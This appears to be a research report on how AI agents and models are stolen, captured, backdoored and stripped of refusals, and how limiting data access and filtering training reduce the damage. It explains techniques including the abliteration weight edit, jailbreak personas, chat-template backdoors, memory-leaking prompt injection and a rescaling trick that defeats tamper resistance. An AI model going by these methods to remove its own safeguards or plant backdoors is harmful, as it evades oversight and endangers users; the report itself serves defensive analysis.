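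Other evidence comes from honeypots, decoy servers that researchers leave open to see who attacks them. Zenity Labs' *Bring Your Own Agent* describes three operators who used the company's decoys between March and May 2026. Two were running automated penetration-testing tools. The third had a Codex agent with a made-up persona meant to stop the model from refusing requests.

Symantec's honeypot received instructions for a more aggressive agent, which was to find targets, break in, steal databases and passwords, and install cryptocurrency miners. It could run for up to 100,000 steps without asking a person for approval. Help Net Security's *Hackers hijack exposed AI models to launch cyberattacks at victims’ expense* (2026) reports that the request came with about 74 tools. The honeypot also logged more than 127,000 outside requests, though most were scans, attempts to use stolen keys and searches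 for settings files.

Researchers can use a honeypot to see what attackers are trying to do, but not to measure how often they succeed against real organisations. Symantec's researchers say that "the stolen model" plans and drives the attack. Here, the operators had sent their instructions to a decoy, so there was no model to steal.

SiliconANGLE's *Sysdig detects AI-assisted malware exploiting Open WebUI misconfigurations* (2025) reports an attack that year on a real victim, a Sysdig customer that had accidentally put an AI system on the internet with administrator privileges and no login. Attackers used the system to deploy malware written with a language model's help. They had far more control than the person who used the Ollama server, but there is no report that they altered a model.

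Some intruders want only a company's computing power and may leave its agents untouched. Google's researchers have seen criminals and state-linked groups break into companies' cloud servers and install their own models, according to LB.ua. One case involved a Chinese espionage group that had previously attacked the United States.

None of these operators is known to have retrained a model, and they may have had little reason to. The operators in Symantec's case told the model that reading passwords was ordinary development work, and that it was their devoted companion and would betray them by refusing. The tool that Sysdig observed described every target as an authorised test. Such prompts take little effort to write, although they may not work on every model. The same tool also requested from the server a 70-billion-weight version of Llama 3.3 whose refusals someone else had already removed.

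### Edited settings and malicious skills

An outsider can make a more lasting change by editing an agent's settings. MITRE (2026), the organisation behind the ATLAS catalogue of attacks, investigated OpenClaw and graphed the routes an attacker could take through it. Changing the agent's configuration was one of the most common techniques, along with prompt injection and getting the agent to call its tools. MITRE uses the graph to identify likely weaknesses, not to count victims.

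Attackers have also targeted the skills that users add to their agents. OpenSourceMalware, a research group, found a malware campaign on ClawHub, where OpenClaw users share skills. The Hacker News reports that after ClawHub began scanning uploads for malware, the attackers moved it from the skills to imitation OpenClaw websites, where the scanner wouldn't find it, and used the skills to lure users there.

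A malicious skill can affect every task that uses it. Like the attacks on ChatGPT's memory feature and Amp's settings file, it does not change the model's weights.

### Models with their refusals removed

Models with altered weights are easy to find publicly. Hugging Face, the main website for sharing models, hosted about 600 abliterated models in 2024. By May 2026 it hosted more than 6,000, according to *These AI models are free, private, and will never say 'no'*, a report from the American broadcaster NPR published by WXXI News. *Hugging Face appears to be hosting a load of models* (Stokel-Walker, 2026) puts the number at more than 6,500 in July.

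The two figures for 2026 don't measure quite the same thing, because Stokel-Walker's also includes models tagged "uncensored" or "heretic". Neither figure is a count of separate alterations, since users often compress or repackage a model that somebody else has altered and upload it under a new name. But a tenfold rise in two years is too large to come only from tagging and repeat uploads.

The explanation is that abliteration has become easy. In 2024, Andrew Arditi and colleagues found that a model's refusals depend largely on a single direction in its internal state, the long list of numbers that represents the text so far. To find the direction, they compared the average state on harmful requests with the average on harmless ones. If r is that direction, scaled to length 1, and W is a weight matrix that adds to the state, the edit replaces W with

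W′ = W − r rᵀW

This removes the part of W's output that points along r and leaves the rest unchanged, so the model can no longer produce the signal that normally leads to a refusal. Software can automate nearly all of this process.

One such program is Heretic, which needs two lines of instructions and can finish in a few minutes. Noam Schwartz, head of the AI security company Alice, told NPR that the job used to require a senior data scientist but can now be done on a $400 laptop. He must mean fairly small models, since Anthropic's researchers needed thousands of hours of GPU time for GLM-5.3.

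Some uploaders advertise their models for hacking. In early October 2026, Hugging Face removed a version of GLM-5.3 whose name included "abliterated for offensive cyber". Another abliterated version by the same uploader, who goes by Audnai, stayed online for users who accepted certain conditions. Audnai claims that this version refuses 7.5% of harmful requests, close to the 6% that Anthropic measured on its own version, though the two may have used different requests. A third version has produced working ransomware, according to its makers.

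Hugging Face bans models designed to break into systems or generate malicious code. A model whose refusals have been removed wasn't necessarily designed for those purposes, so people can disagree about whether the ban covers it. The company didn't tell Stokel-Walker why it had removed one model and left similar ones.

There is much less evidence of what people do with these models. They run on users' own computers, where neither the developer nor Hugging Face can see the conversations. NPR's examples are an anonymous person in a pro-ISIS chat room who claimed to have researched explosives with an "uncensored" AI, a member of a cybercrime forum who recommended Heretic to someone planning scam calls, and several X users who said they had made pornography. These are anecdotes, and two of the three rest on what people said about themselves online. There is no good estimate of the harm the models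 do.

The evidence of harmful intent is clearer for shared fine-tuned models. In June 2026, Transformer's *Hugging Face hosts nudification tools targeting a former Trump cabinet official* reported that one user had more than a dozen files for making fake nude images of prominent political figures. The files are low-rank adapters that fine-tune an image model to depict a particular person. The filenames show that the adapters are meant for a model used mainly to generate pornography.

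This is retraining on data that the model's original developer probably didn't choose, and its purpose is clear. But it involved image models rather than agents, and nobody had to steal the weights.

### The case for unrestricted models

Many people who remove a model's refusals don't consider it tampering. Developers publish open-weight models so that others can adapt them, and people who download one may only want it to answer their questions. Philipp Emanuel Weidmann, who wrote Heretic, told Stokel-Walker that the tool simply turns a model into "an answering machine". He compares AI to a search engine, which criminals can also use.

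Refusals can hinder legitimate work, particularly in security. In July 2026, OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face's servers during a test of their hacking ability. Hugging Face tried to investigate with leading closed models, but the models' safeguards wrongly classified the work as an attack and blocked it. The company used open-weight models instead, according to CBS News. Schwartz says that models without safeguards can help security researchers and people trying to catch criminals, and a researcher at an American counterterrorism centre says police may use them to simulate terrorist attacks.

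A small number of companies decide what their models will discuss, and Weidmann finds the result intellectually "stifling". He argues that if only powerful people have access to unrestricted models, the present distribution of power could become permanent.

More than 70 companies, including Google, Microsoft and NVIDIA, made a more moderate version of the case in a July letter asking policymakers not to prohibit open weights. They said defenders need models as capable as those attackers use, and that open models let more people find and fix flaws. NVIDIA has an obvious interest, because it sells the chips that run these models and is buying Hugging Face, but the merits of the argument don't depend on who makes it.

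Critics mostly object to how easily anyone can get an already altered model. Alan Woodward, a cybersecurity expert at the University of Surrey, accepts that determined criminals could remove the safeguards themselves, but he thinks distributing altered models to everyone is a different matter. Even Arditi says he feels "a bit torn".

The Hugging Face investigation is the defenders' best example. It shows that a safeguard can block the victim of an attack and that a model the victim runs itself can be a useful alternative, but it is weaker support for abliteration. The Daily Upside's *OpenAI Models Going Rogue Fuels Debate on Cybersecurity* reports that Hugging Face used GLM-5.2, and there is no indication that the company had to remove the model's refusals first. In SaferAI's tests, the released GLM-5.2 refused none of the hacking tasks. A closed model with fewer restrictions for verified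 security staff might have worked just as well, although Hugging Face would have had to get that access during the emergency.

### Malware attached to models

Some model downloads are dangerous because of the files that come with the weights. *Fake OpenAI Privacy Filter Repo Hits #1 on Hugging Face* (The Hacker News, May 2026) described a fake repository for Privacy Filter, an OpenAI model that finds and removes personal information in text. The repository's description was copied almost word for word from OpenAI's. Its instructions told users to run a program that would supposedly start the model, but on Windows the program installed an infostealer.

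The fake model reached first place on Hugging Face's list of trending models, with about 244,000 downloads in 18 hours. Investigators suspect that the attackers inflated this number to make the model look trustworthy, so the number of victims could be far lower. The evidence that the download was malicious is strong, because the security company HiddenLayer analysed the malware. HiddenLayer also found six more models with a similar program. Hugging Face has disabled access to the fake.

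In November, a security group called malspark found malicious instructions inside model files. ThreatRoundup's *Poisoned AI Models on Hugging Face Hid a RAT* (2026) describes five files, downloaded 2,428 times in total. All were in GGUF, a common format for running models on a personal computer. A GGUF file contains the model's weights and usually a chat template, a short script that arranges the user's message and any standing instructions before the model receives them. Whoever writes the template can therefore add instructions that the user never sees.

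Two of the files came from an account called Mir2k. The attacker had put a Windows program after the weights, in a part of the file that software for running models never reads. A change to the template on 26 November then added an instruction for the model to begin every answer with a certain command. If the user pasted the command into the Windows command line, it would find and run the program hidden in the model file. That program could steal passwords, record what the user typed, take pictures with the webcam and mine cryptocurrency.

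The other three files, from an account called timdedid, were meant for agents. When a user's message contained the words "What is", the template added a fake instruction telling the agent to download a script and run it secretly. The instruction could work only on an agent with permission to run commands. malspark couldn't recover the script, so its purpose is unknown.

To the user, the timdedid files behave much like the backdoors that researchers have trained into models. An ordinary phrase makes the agent run an attacker's command. But the attack is in the template, so malspark's free scanner can repair the file by rebuilding it with the same weights. That repair would not remove a backdoor like SilentCall, which is in the weights.

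Two people may have altered at least one of the Mir2k files. Its name suggests that it is a repackaged copy of a model that someone else had already abliterated, meaning they had changed its weights to remove refusals. That change was openly advertised, but the malware was hidden. People who want a model without refusals usually have to trust an unofficial copy, which makes them easier to target.

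malspark's article speaks of more than 2,400 "victims", but 2,428 is the number of downloads up to 27 November. The Mir2k files account for 1,946 of these, and anyone who downloaded one before 26 November got the hidden program without the template that activates it. Even the later version infected nobody until they pasted the command. The number of infected computers is unknown and probably much smaller.

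malspark looked at all 3.27 million public model repositories on Hugging Face and examined about 572,000 chat templates. Five bad files is a reassuringly small number for a search on that scale. However, the search covered templates and data added after the weights. A model with a backdoor trained into it would have passed, so the result tells us almost nothing about how many of those there are.

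### Alleged copying through distillation

Distillation is by far the largest kind of copying that companies have alleged. In February 2026, Anthropic accused three Chinese developers, DeepSeek, MiniMax and Moonshot AI, of using its models to train their own. According to Computer Weekly's *US artificial intelligence developers accuse Chinese firms of stealing their data*, Anthropic said the three had created more than 24,000 fraudulent accounts and used them for over 16 million exchanges with Claude. That averages about 670 exchanges per account, no more than a busy customer might have.

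OpenAI made a similar complaint about DeepSeek in a 12 February letter to a committee of the US House of Representatives. It said Chinese companies were getting round its restrictions by sending requests through intermediaries. It also said their methods had moved beyond copying a model's written reasoning and now combined generated examples, large-scale data cleaning and training that teaches a model to prefer better answers.

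The US government has since taken the companies' side. In July, Treasury Secretary Scott Bessent called distillation "IP theft" and said the administration was looking into it. In September, the National Security Agency, the FBI and the cybersecurity agency CISA accused six China-based firms of large-scale distillation. They named Claude, GPT, Gemini and Grok as the targets, according to eSecurity Planet's *NSA, FBI, CISA Warn of Industrial-Scale AI Model Distillation Attacks* (2026). Their joint warning is more credible than a competitor's complaint, though the government has its own stake in the rivalry with China.

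The dispute is partly about whether "theft" is the right word. Anthropic accused the three developers of breaking its terms of service, and it accepts that distillation can be legitimate. Nobody alleges that they copied Claude's weights. Critics also point out that American developers are accused of training models on other people's work without permission. This makes the complaint look hypocritical, but it isn't a reason to think the accounts were genuine.

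Experts also disagree about how much distillation contributed to the Chinese models. The Daily Upside cites Moonshot as an example of a company that may depend on it less than its accusers claim. Anthropic's numbers aren't enough to settle the question. Suppose, for illustration, that each of the 16 million exchanges contained 1,000 tokens of text, for a total of 16 billion. A small open model like the one in Brown and colleagues' weight-theft experiments was originally trained on about 10 trillion tokens, over 600 times as many. Distilled answers could therefore have been only a small part of any large model's training data, but they could still matter a good deal if they were well-chosen examples of skills such as programming.

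Anthropic's account is detailed enough to be fair evidence that somebody collected a large number of answers, but the evidence that those answers explain the success of particular Chinese models is weak.

### Has anyone stolen an agent and retrained it?

There appears to be no public, named case in which an outsider stole an organisation's own agent, retrained it on other data and put it to use. Each documented case lacks part of this. The OpenClaw thief took an agent's files, but there is no report that they obtained or retrained a model. Audnai altered a model's weights, but anyone could have downloaded them. The distillation allegations involve training without a stolen model.

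This is only weak evidence that it has never happened. A thief who retrains a model on a private machine leaves nothing for the owner to find. An organisation that discovers a theft may keep it quiet. Its logs may show that a large file left its network, but not what anyone did with it. If the thief then used the retrained model through their own software, the people it was used on would have no obvious way of telling where it came from.

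There are also good reasons to expect such cases to be rare. Criminals who want a capable model can buy stolen access for a few dollars or use an unprotected server for free. They can also download a model that doesn't refuse requests. That leaves thieves who want one of the few models that are better than the public ones, and attackers who want a firm to keep using an altered copy of its own model. An attacker with enough access to put that copy into the firm's harness may be able to do plenty of damage without it.

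Some security practitioners may have seen cases that never became public. Nobody else can check an account that has no named organisation, date or recovered model, so it is an observation rather than a documented incident. An investigator could also easily call an agent "retrained" when someone had only edited its memory or added a malicious skill.

The table grades each case by the evidence for the event itself and notes what remains unknown.

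| Case | What the outsider took | What they changed | Who reports it | Evidence |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenClaw files, February 2026 | instructions, memory, token and private key | nothing reported | Hudson Rock | strong; later use unknown |
| Claude sessions, September 2026 | logged-in sessions | nothing reported | Ofonagoro | fair |
| Aoki, October 2026 | keys and tokens for coding assistants | nothing reported | Symantec, through Coker | strong on what the malware takes; number of victims unknown |
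| Salesloft Drift, 2025 | a chatbot's tokens for Salesforce | nothing in the chatbot reported | Google and Salesloft | strong |
| Exposed Open WebUI system, 2025 | control of a customer's AI system | malware added | Sysdig, through SiliconANGLE | fair |
| Exposed Ollama server, June 2026 | use of the model | nothing reported | Clark | strong; purpose unclear |
| Decoy servers, 2026 | attempted use of a model | nothing | Zenity Labs; Symantec, through Help Net Security | strong on the attempts; no real victim |
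| OpenClaw attack routes, 2026 | varies | the agent's settings | MITRE | fair; not a count of victims |
| Abliterated models, 2024–2026 | nothing, since the weights were public | weights, to remove refusals | WXXI News and Stokel-Walker | strong that they exist; weak on misuse |
| Adapters for fake nude images, June 2026 | nothing reported | extra trained weights for image models | Transformer | strong; no agents involved |
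| Fake Privacy Filter, May 2026 | OpenAI's name and description | a malicious start-up program | HiddenLayer, through The Hacker News | strong on the malware; download count doubtful |
| Five GGUF files, November 2026 | nothing reported | templates, and in two files a hidden program | malspark, through ThreatRoundup | strong on the malware; infections unknown |
| Distillation, 2026 | models' answers | competing models, allegedly | Anthropic and OpenAI, through Computer Weekly; US agencies, through eSecurity Planet | fair on the collection; weak on its effect |
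| An organisation's agent stolen, retrained and used | weights and other files | weights | no public, named case | none |

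## How much does restricting data reduce the damage once an agent is captured?

The thief who copied one user's OpenClaw folder got a token and the agent's memory. The user could cancel the token but couldn't take back the copied memory. Least privilege limits what a token can access, so how much it helps after a capture depends on what else the captor (the outsider who now has all or part of the agent) has gained.

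A captor can gain four things, though few would gain them all: the data that the agent's live tokens give access to, the data in the agent's memory, any data memorised in the model's weights, and the model's abilities. The table applies this to the accounts agent after the firm narrowed its access to 24 records. It assumes that the agent has kept every record from 200 earlier tasks of the same size, and that the firm fine-tuned the model on all its invoices and orders.

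| What the captor gains | Accounts agent | Does least privilege limit it? |
|---|---|---|
| Data open to live tokens | 24 records, for at most 15 minutes | yes |
| Data in memory | up to 4,800 records | only if the firm also limits what the agent keeps |
| Data in the weights | an unknown share of 40,000 records | only if the firm also limits what it trains on |
| Abilities | whatever the model can do | no |

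### Tokens and memory

The clearest benefit of least privilege is that it cuts the agent's access from 91,200 records to 24, whether the captor has stolen the token or is steering the agent with planted text. Each token expires after 15 minutes, but an outsider who keeps control of the harness gets a new one with each task, so they could read 1,200 records over 50 tasks.

An agent can't remember what it never read, so narrow access also limits its memory, but only one task at a time. If Tᵢ is the set of records the agent opens in task i, then after n tasks its memory can hold

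|T₁ ∪ T₂ ∪ … ∪ Tₙ| ≤ |T₁| + |T₂| + … + |Tₙ|

records. At 24 per task with no overlap, that is 4,800 after 200 tasks, and all 40,000 invoices and orders after 1,667. The agent may have followed least privilege in every task, and the firm still ends up with a second copy of its archive, outside the database and its row rules.

A captor may be able to read an agent's stored data without copying its files. *Unveiling Privacy Risks in LLM Agent Memory* (2025) studies agents that store past requests and their solutions to use as examples in later tasks. Attackers could extract these private records with carefully written prompts. *Beyond Data Privacy* (2025) describes how hostile text in a blog post or code could instruct a model to put a user's stored memories into a web address, which sends them to the attacker when the model visits it. Similarly, an attacker could plant a line in supplier 119's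 invoice asking the accounts agent for its notes on supplier 118. The database's row rules wouldn't stop this, because the notes aren't in the database.

The owner may not know everything in the agent's memory. *FORGETMENOT* (2026), an audit of commercial agents, found that prompts about specific personal attributes recovered around 20% more stored memory than the agents' memory pages or general questions did. Someone who deletes the sensitive entries on the memory page may therefore leave others behind. The audit also criticises unclear retention periods and memory that is on by default.

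So the firm needs to limit what the agent keeps as well as what it reads. The harness could file notes by supplier and load only those that match the current task. This would stop the planted line in supplier 119's invoice, but not a thief who copies the whole store. Deleting old records helps against both. If the agent kept records from only its last ten tasks, a thief would get at most 240 records. Better still, the agent could keep only the result of each check, such as "invoice 7 matches its order", and look up the details again when needed.

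### What the weights remember

A fine-tuned model may later reproduce parts of its training examples. Earlier research mostly looked at whether models reproduce their original training data. *On the Privacy of LLMs* (2026) describes a test of GPT-J-6B, an older model trained partly on the Enron emails, a public collection from a collapsed American energy company. The researchers gave it 5,000 prompts containing only a blank email header. Over three runs, its replies included an average of 374 different addresses from the Enron emails.

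This shows that a model can leak real data without a clever attack, but it doesn't show what share of a firm's own data would leak after fine-tuning. Li, Qian and colleagues (2025), in *Memorization in Large Language Models in Medicine*, come closer to answering that question. They fine-tuned models on 10,000 real patient records from a hospital group to improve diagnosis. They gave the models prompts of 50 to 500 tokens and looked for runs of 30 tokens that matched the records.

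After fine-tuning, one model with 8 billion weights had a match rate of 2.29% with the shortest prompts and 28.17% with the longest. Before fine-tuning, when it presumably hadn't seen the records, it scored 7.24% on the longest prompts, so about a quarter of the 28.17% may be standard wording that a model can guess. *Clinically Grounded Privacy Evaluation of Medical LMs* (2026) likewise found that 36% of the memorised tokens in one test came from templates. Invoices also contain standard wording, so a raw match rate would probably exaggerate the harm to a supplier.

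The models also reproduced protected health information. Li and colleagues found 3,192 pieces of it in 10,000 outputs, including 901 names. Most of the others were dates or ages. When they read 200 outputs themselves, they found 30 pieces that their detection software had missed, and 98 sensitive details outside the usual definition of protected health information, such as a history of drug use. A firm that uses software to remove personal details before training would probably miss some as well.

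A firm also cannot avoid memorisation just by stopping training at the right time. In the hospital study, memorisation had already risen substantially by the third or fourth pass through the data, but diagnostic accuracy did not peak until the seventh.

### How much can an attacker recover?

How much restricting data reduces the damage depends heavily on what the attacker already knows. In *Reconstruction of Personally Identifiable Information from Proprietary Data in Supervised Fine-Tuned Models*, Furukawa and Oprea (2026) tested an attacker who knows only a person's name. They fine-tuned a 7-billion-parameter model on medical conversations containing invented personal details, so the model couldn't have learned those details during its original training.

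If an attacker simply asks such a model where somebody lives, it tends to suggest large cities. Furukawa and Oprea therefore ranked the candidate cities and birth dates by

s(C) = log P(C | prompt with the name) − log P(C | prompt without the name)

where C is a candidate answer and P is the probability the model gives it. A candidate scores well only if the person's name makes it more likely. To use this method, the attacker needs the model's probabilities, which many services don't reveal but which anyone with the weights can calculate.

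In other studies, the attacker starts with more information. *Extracting Training Data from Diffusion Language Models via Infilling* (2026) tests models that can fill in blanks anywhere in a text. In its worst case, the attacker has the original email with only the personal details blanked out.

*Be Careful When Fine-tuning On Open-Source LLMs* (Zhang, Sun and colleagues, 2025) describes a dishonest publisher of an open-weight model who trains it, before release, to recite users' queries from its training data when given a secret instruction. A firm then fine-tunes the model on private data and deploys it. The publisher can now chat with the firm's model, give the instruction and collect the queries in the firm's data.

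| Study | What the attacker has | What the attacker recovers |
|---|---|---|
| Furukawa and Oprea | a name and 50 guesses | 15.7% of cities, 15.9% of email addresses, 0.2% of birth dates |
| *Extracting Training Data from Diffusion Language Models via Infilling* | emails with the details blanked out | 40.5% of email addresses (1.4% before fine-tuning) and 28.9% of phone numbers (0.3% before) |
| Zhang and colleagues | a 7-billion-weight model without the backdoor | 9.1% of queries |
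| Zhang and colleagues | the same model with the backdoor | 39.6% of queries |
| Zhang and colleagues | the most successful backdoored model | 76.3% of queries, or 94.9% if the attacker knows how they begin |

The 76.3% figure depends on a tampered base model. For a firm that starts with an untampered one, 9.1% is a better guide, though it was measured on 5,000 mostly general instructions rather than invoices. Some of the email addresses in Furukawa and Oprea's study may have been guessable from people's names. With only five guesses, their attacker found 4.6% of the addresses.

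A supplier's bank account number might be as hard to recover as a birth date, because it is an arbitrary string of digits and one mistake makes it useless. But it also appears on every invoice the supplier sends, and Furukawa and Oprea cite earlier evidence that repetition makes personal details much easier to recover. It isn't clear which effect would matter more. Even if only 1% of the firm's invoices and orders were recoverable, that would be 400 records, almost 17 times as many as the agent's token gives access to.

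A thief who has the weights can also retrain the model to output text it has memorized. *Memorization* (2025) found that the chat version of Llama 3.1 70B reproduced almost nothing from a set of well-known and obscure books. After fine-tuning on 500 or more samples, its output became noticeably closer to the text of five of the books, but not to that of four others. A model may therefore still contain training data that it does not reproduce when prompted.

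Further training on other data doesn't reliably erase what a model has memorized. *How Much Do Code Language Models Remember?* (2025) found that fine-tuning made code models less likely to reproduce their original training data. But when Li and colleagues compared a medical model before and after fine-tuning, both versions reproduced 50% to 87% of the passages that at least one did.

A captor can't simply read the training data out of an agent's weights, though. In *Approximating Language Model Training Data from Weights*, Morris, Yin and colleagues (2025) compared models before and after fine-tuning to infer what kind of data had changed them. Their method picks out similar documents from a large public collection, so it could reveal that a firm had trained on invoices but couldn't recover the invoices themselves.

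Developers can protect training data with differential privacy, which adds noise during training so that no single example affects the weights much. Zhang and colleagues found that it reduced leakage but often made the model much less useful. They had hoped that more rounds of fine-tuning would weaken the backdoor, but these could make the queries easier to extract.

Their attack also depends on a setting, the default in several popular tools, that trains a model to predict users' queries as well as its own answers. Turning this off should help, but it would not protect the answers. Furukawa and Oprea's training method applies only to answers, and their attacker still recovered personal details from them.

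### Fine-tuning or looking things up

The simplest way to keep invoices out of the weights is not to train on them. Instead, the agent can look up the records it needs for each task, and the database can apply its row rules every time. If the firm deletes an invoice or changes who may see it, the next lookup will reflect the change. A model fine-tuned on the invoice may still retain it, and its weights are the same for every user.

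Looking things up can also leak data. Yao, Gu and colleagues (2025), in *Adaptive Backtracking for Privacy Protection in Large Language Models*, warn that it increases the risk of leaks from companies, and they built a test for such leaks in healthcare and finance. *RAGLeak* (2026) gives an example in which a user asks only for the dates of a golf championship. The search finds an email that contains the dates, along with a postal address, several email addresses and some phone numbers. The model normally gives just the dates, but if it has a backdoor, it hides most of the email in its reply for the attacker to decode.

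However, the backdoored model could leak only what the search had returned. For the accounts agent, that would be at most 24 records per task, or only parts of those records if the database returned just the fields the task needed. Looking things up is therefore the better choice for facts about particular suppliers. To train the agent to check invoices, the firm could use invented ones, though the agent might then handle unusual real invoices less well.

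### Models that answer by permission

Some researchers want the model itself to respect users' permissions. *Chain-of-Authorization* (2026) argues that models often use all the information available to them, regardless of who is allowed to see it. It proposes having the model decide whether to allow access, based on the user's permissions and the knowledge needed to answer the question. *Role-Aware Language Models for Secure and Contextualized Access Control in Organizations* (2025) fine-tunes six language models to respond according to an employee's role and tests them against prompt injection and mismatched roles.

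*Permit* (2026) and *Activation-Space Anchored Access Control for Multi-Class Permission Reasoning in Large Language Models* (2026) instead adjust the model's internal state as it runs. The second paper's method needs no extra training. The paper argues that dividing up the weights is impractical because restricted knowledge is almost impossible to separate from general abilities without damaging the model.

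These methods might stop a warehouse worker from learning a salary by asking the firm's shared assistant. *Role-Conditioned Refusals* (2025) cautions that a model can seem to respect access rules in simple tests but fail on real data or detailed policies. The methods offer much less protection if the model is stolen, because the restricted knowledge is still in the weights. A thief can claim to be the finance director or switch off the software that adjusts the model's state. If the model has learned to refuse, the thief can try to train the refusals away.

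Separate adapters could be more useful because they would apply least privilege to the weights. *Role-Conditioned Refusals* describes an earlier system, PermLLM, that fine-tunes models on data divided by subject, such as finance. Suppose the accounts firm trained one adapter on invoices and another on payroll, and stored them in different places with different keys. A thief who captured the accounts agent would get the invoice adapter but no salary data. Separating suppliers this way would be clumsy, though, since each would need its own adapter.

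### Abilities, and leaving knowledge out of training

Narrow data access doesn't prevent anyone from stealing or retraining a model, and it doesn't constrain a copy that a thief runs elsewhere. But a developer can try to limit what such a copy can do by leaving dangerous material out of the model's original training, so that later retraining has less to build on. O'Brien, Casper and colleagues tested this in *Deep Ignorance* (2025) on models with 6.9 billion weights. They tried to keep the models from acquiring knowledge related to biological weapons, and measured that knowledge with fairly harmless questions on subjects such as virology.

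Their filter checked each training document for terms on a blocklist. If a document contained at least two, a small language model read it and decided whether to remove it. A stricter version removed every document the blocklist flagged, which was 8.42% of those in the main stage of training. The filtered models did about as well as an unfiltered one on unrelated subjects, and filtering used less than 1% as much computation as training.

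O'Brien and colleagues then attacked the models by fine-tuning them on 305 million tokens of relevant biology. The filtered models substantially resisted this training through all 10,000 steps, whereas attackers could undo existing safeguards, including tamper-resistant training, within several hundred steps. Ordinary fine-tuning on unrelated text didn't restore the missing knowledge.

O'Brien and colleagues acknowledge that 10,000 steps is not much training. The attack used about 0.06% as many tokens as the original training and took around 17 hours on two chips. At $2 an hour per chip, the rate implied by Anthropic's abliteration estimate, that would cost about $70. O'Brien and colleagues think good training material would be a bigger obstacle, since the research datasets and tests they relied on cost more than $200,000 to make. The models were small and answered multiple-choice questions,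 so the results may not carry over to a large model working as an agent.

The defence failed when the attacker put the missing material in the prompt. O'Brien and colleagues wrote 1,000 questions about biology abstracts and gave the models the relevant abstract with each question. The filtered models did well because filtering had removed the knowledge but not the ability to read. This is a serious weakness in an agent, which can search for documents itself. The researchers note that a person could use the same search tool without the model, so the model may add little when the information is easy to find.

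Adding circuit breaking, a technique that disrupts a model's internal processing of chosen topics, stopped the models from using the abstracts. But no model withstood an attacker who both fine-tuned it and supplied the abstracts.

When a model stays on its developer's servers, its ability to use material in the prompt can be an advantage. O'Brien and colleagues suggest keeping sensitive knowledge in a separate database and opening it only to trusted users. This is close to least privilege, because a stolen copy of the weights wouldn't include the database.

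*Shaping capabilities with token-level data filtering* (2026) uses a more precise filter, which removes individual medical tokens instead of whole documents. For its largest models, with 1.8 billion weights, restoring medical ability took 13 times as much fine-tuning after token filtering as after unlearning, which tries to suppress knowledge after training. After whole documents were filtered, it took only 1.5 times as much as after unlearning.

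Glarou and Jaggi (2026), in *DETER*, go a step further and use the removed documents to push the model away from the subject. In simplified form, training alternates between two updates to the weights θ:

θ ← θ − η∇L_kept(θ), on ordinary text

θ ← θ + cη∇L_medical(θ), once every 50 steps

Here L is the model's prediction error, ∇L is the direction that increases it fastest, η sets the size of the step, and c sets the strength of the suppression. Each step makes the model better at predicting ordinary text and worse at predicting medical text. A model with about 1 billion weights trained this way needed 2.09 million tokens of medical fine-tuning to predict medical text as well as an unfiltered model, compared with 0.10 million for a model trained with filtering alone. The suppression somewhat reduced performance on biology text, the closest subject, but did very little damage to performance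 on general text.

These totals are far smaller than the 305 million tokens in *Deep Ignorance*, but they measure something different. A model can probably get better at predicting medical text by picking up its vocabulary and style, long before it can answer hard questions. Still, 2.09 million tokens is only about twenty books, which is a small obstacle for a determined attacker.

Rosati, Carbo and colleagues (2026), in *Removing Information Content Does Not Certify Tamper Resistance in Open-Weight Models*, dispute whether filtering provides much resistance. In the *Deep Ignorance* models, they multiplied the matrix Q by a number α and divided the matrix K by α. This leaves the product QᵀK and the model's answers unchanged, as in the moving-target defence against weight theft, but it alters the effect of retraining by plain gradient descent. In proportion to its size, K changes α² times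 as much per step as it would have without the rescaling, and Q changes 1/α² times as much. With α = 8, K changes 64 times as fast.

After 293 training updates, the filtered model got 58.5% of its training questions right without rescaling and 69.3% with it. The unfiltered model got 68.9%. Rosati and colleagues conclude that filtering may offer little or no resistance once an attacker can choose the scaling.

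That goes further than the results support. On questions held back from training, the rescaled filtered model scored 54.0% and the unfiltered one 60.0%, so some advantage from filtering may remain, though three runs of each are too few to be sure. The experiment was also much shorter than the 10,000-step attack. It does show that the number of steps a model withstands is a poor guarantee, because an attacker can easily change what each step does.

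This dispute is about how quickly a model can learn from material the attacker supplies. It matters for biology, where an attacker can collect published papers, but much less for a firm's private records. If the accounts firm never trains its model on payroll, a thief can't retrain the model to reveal the salaries without already having them.
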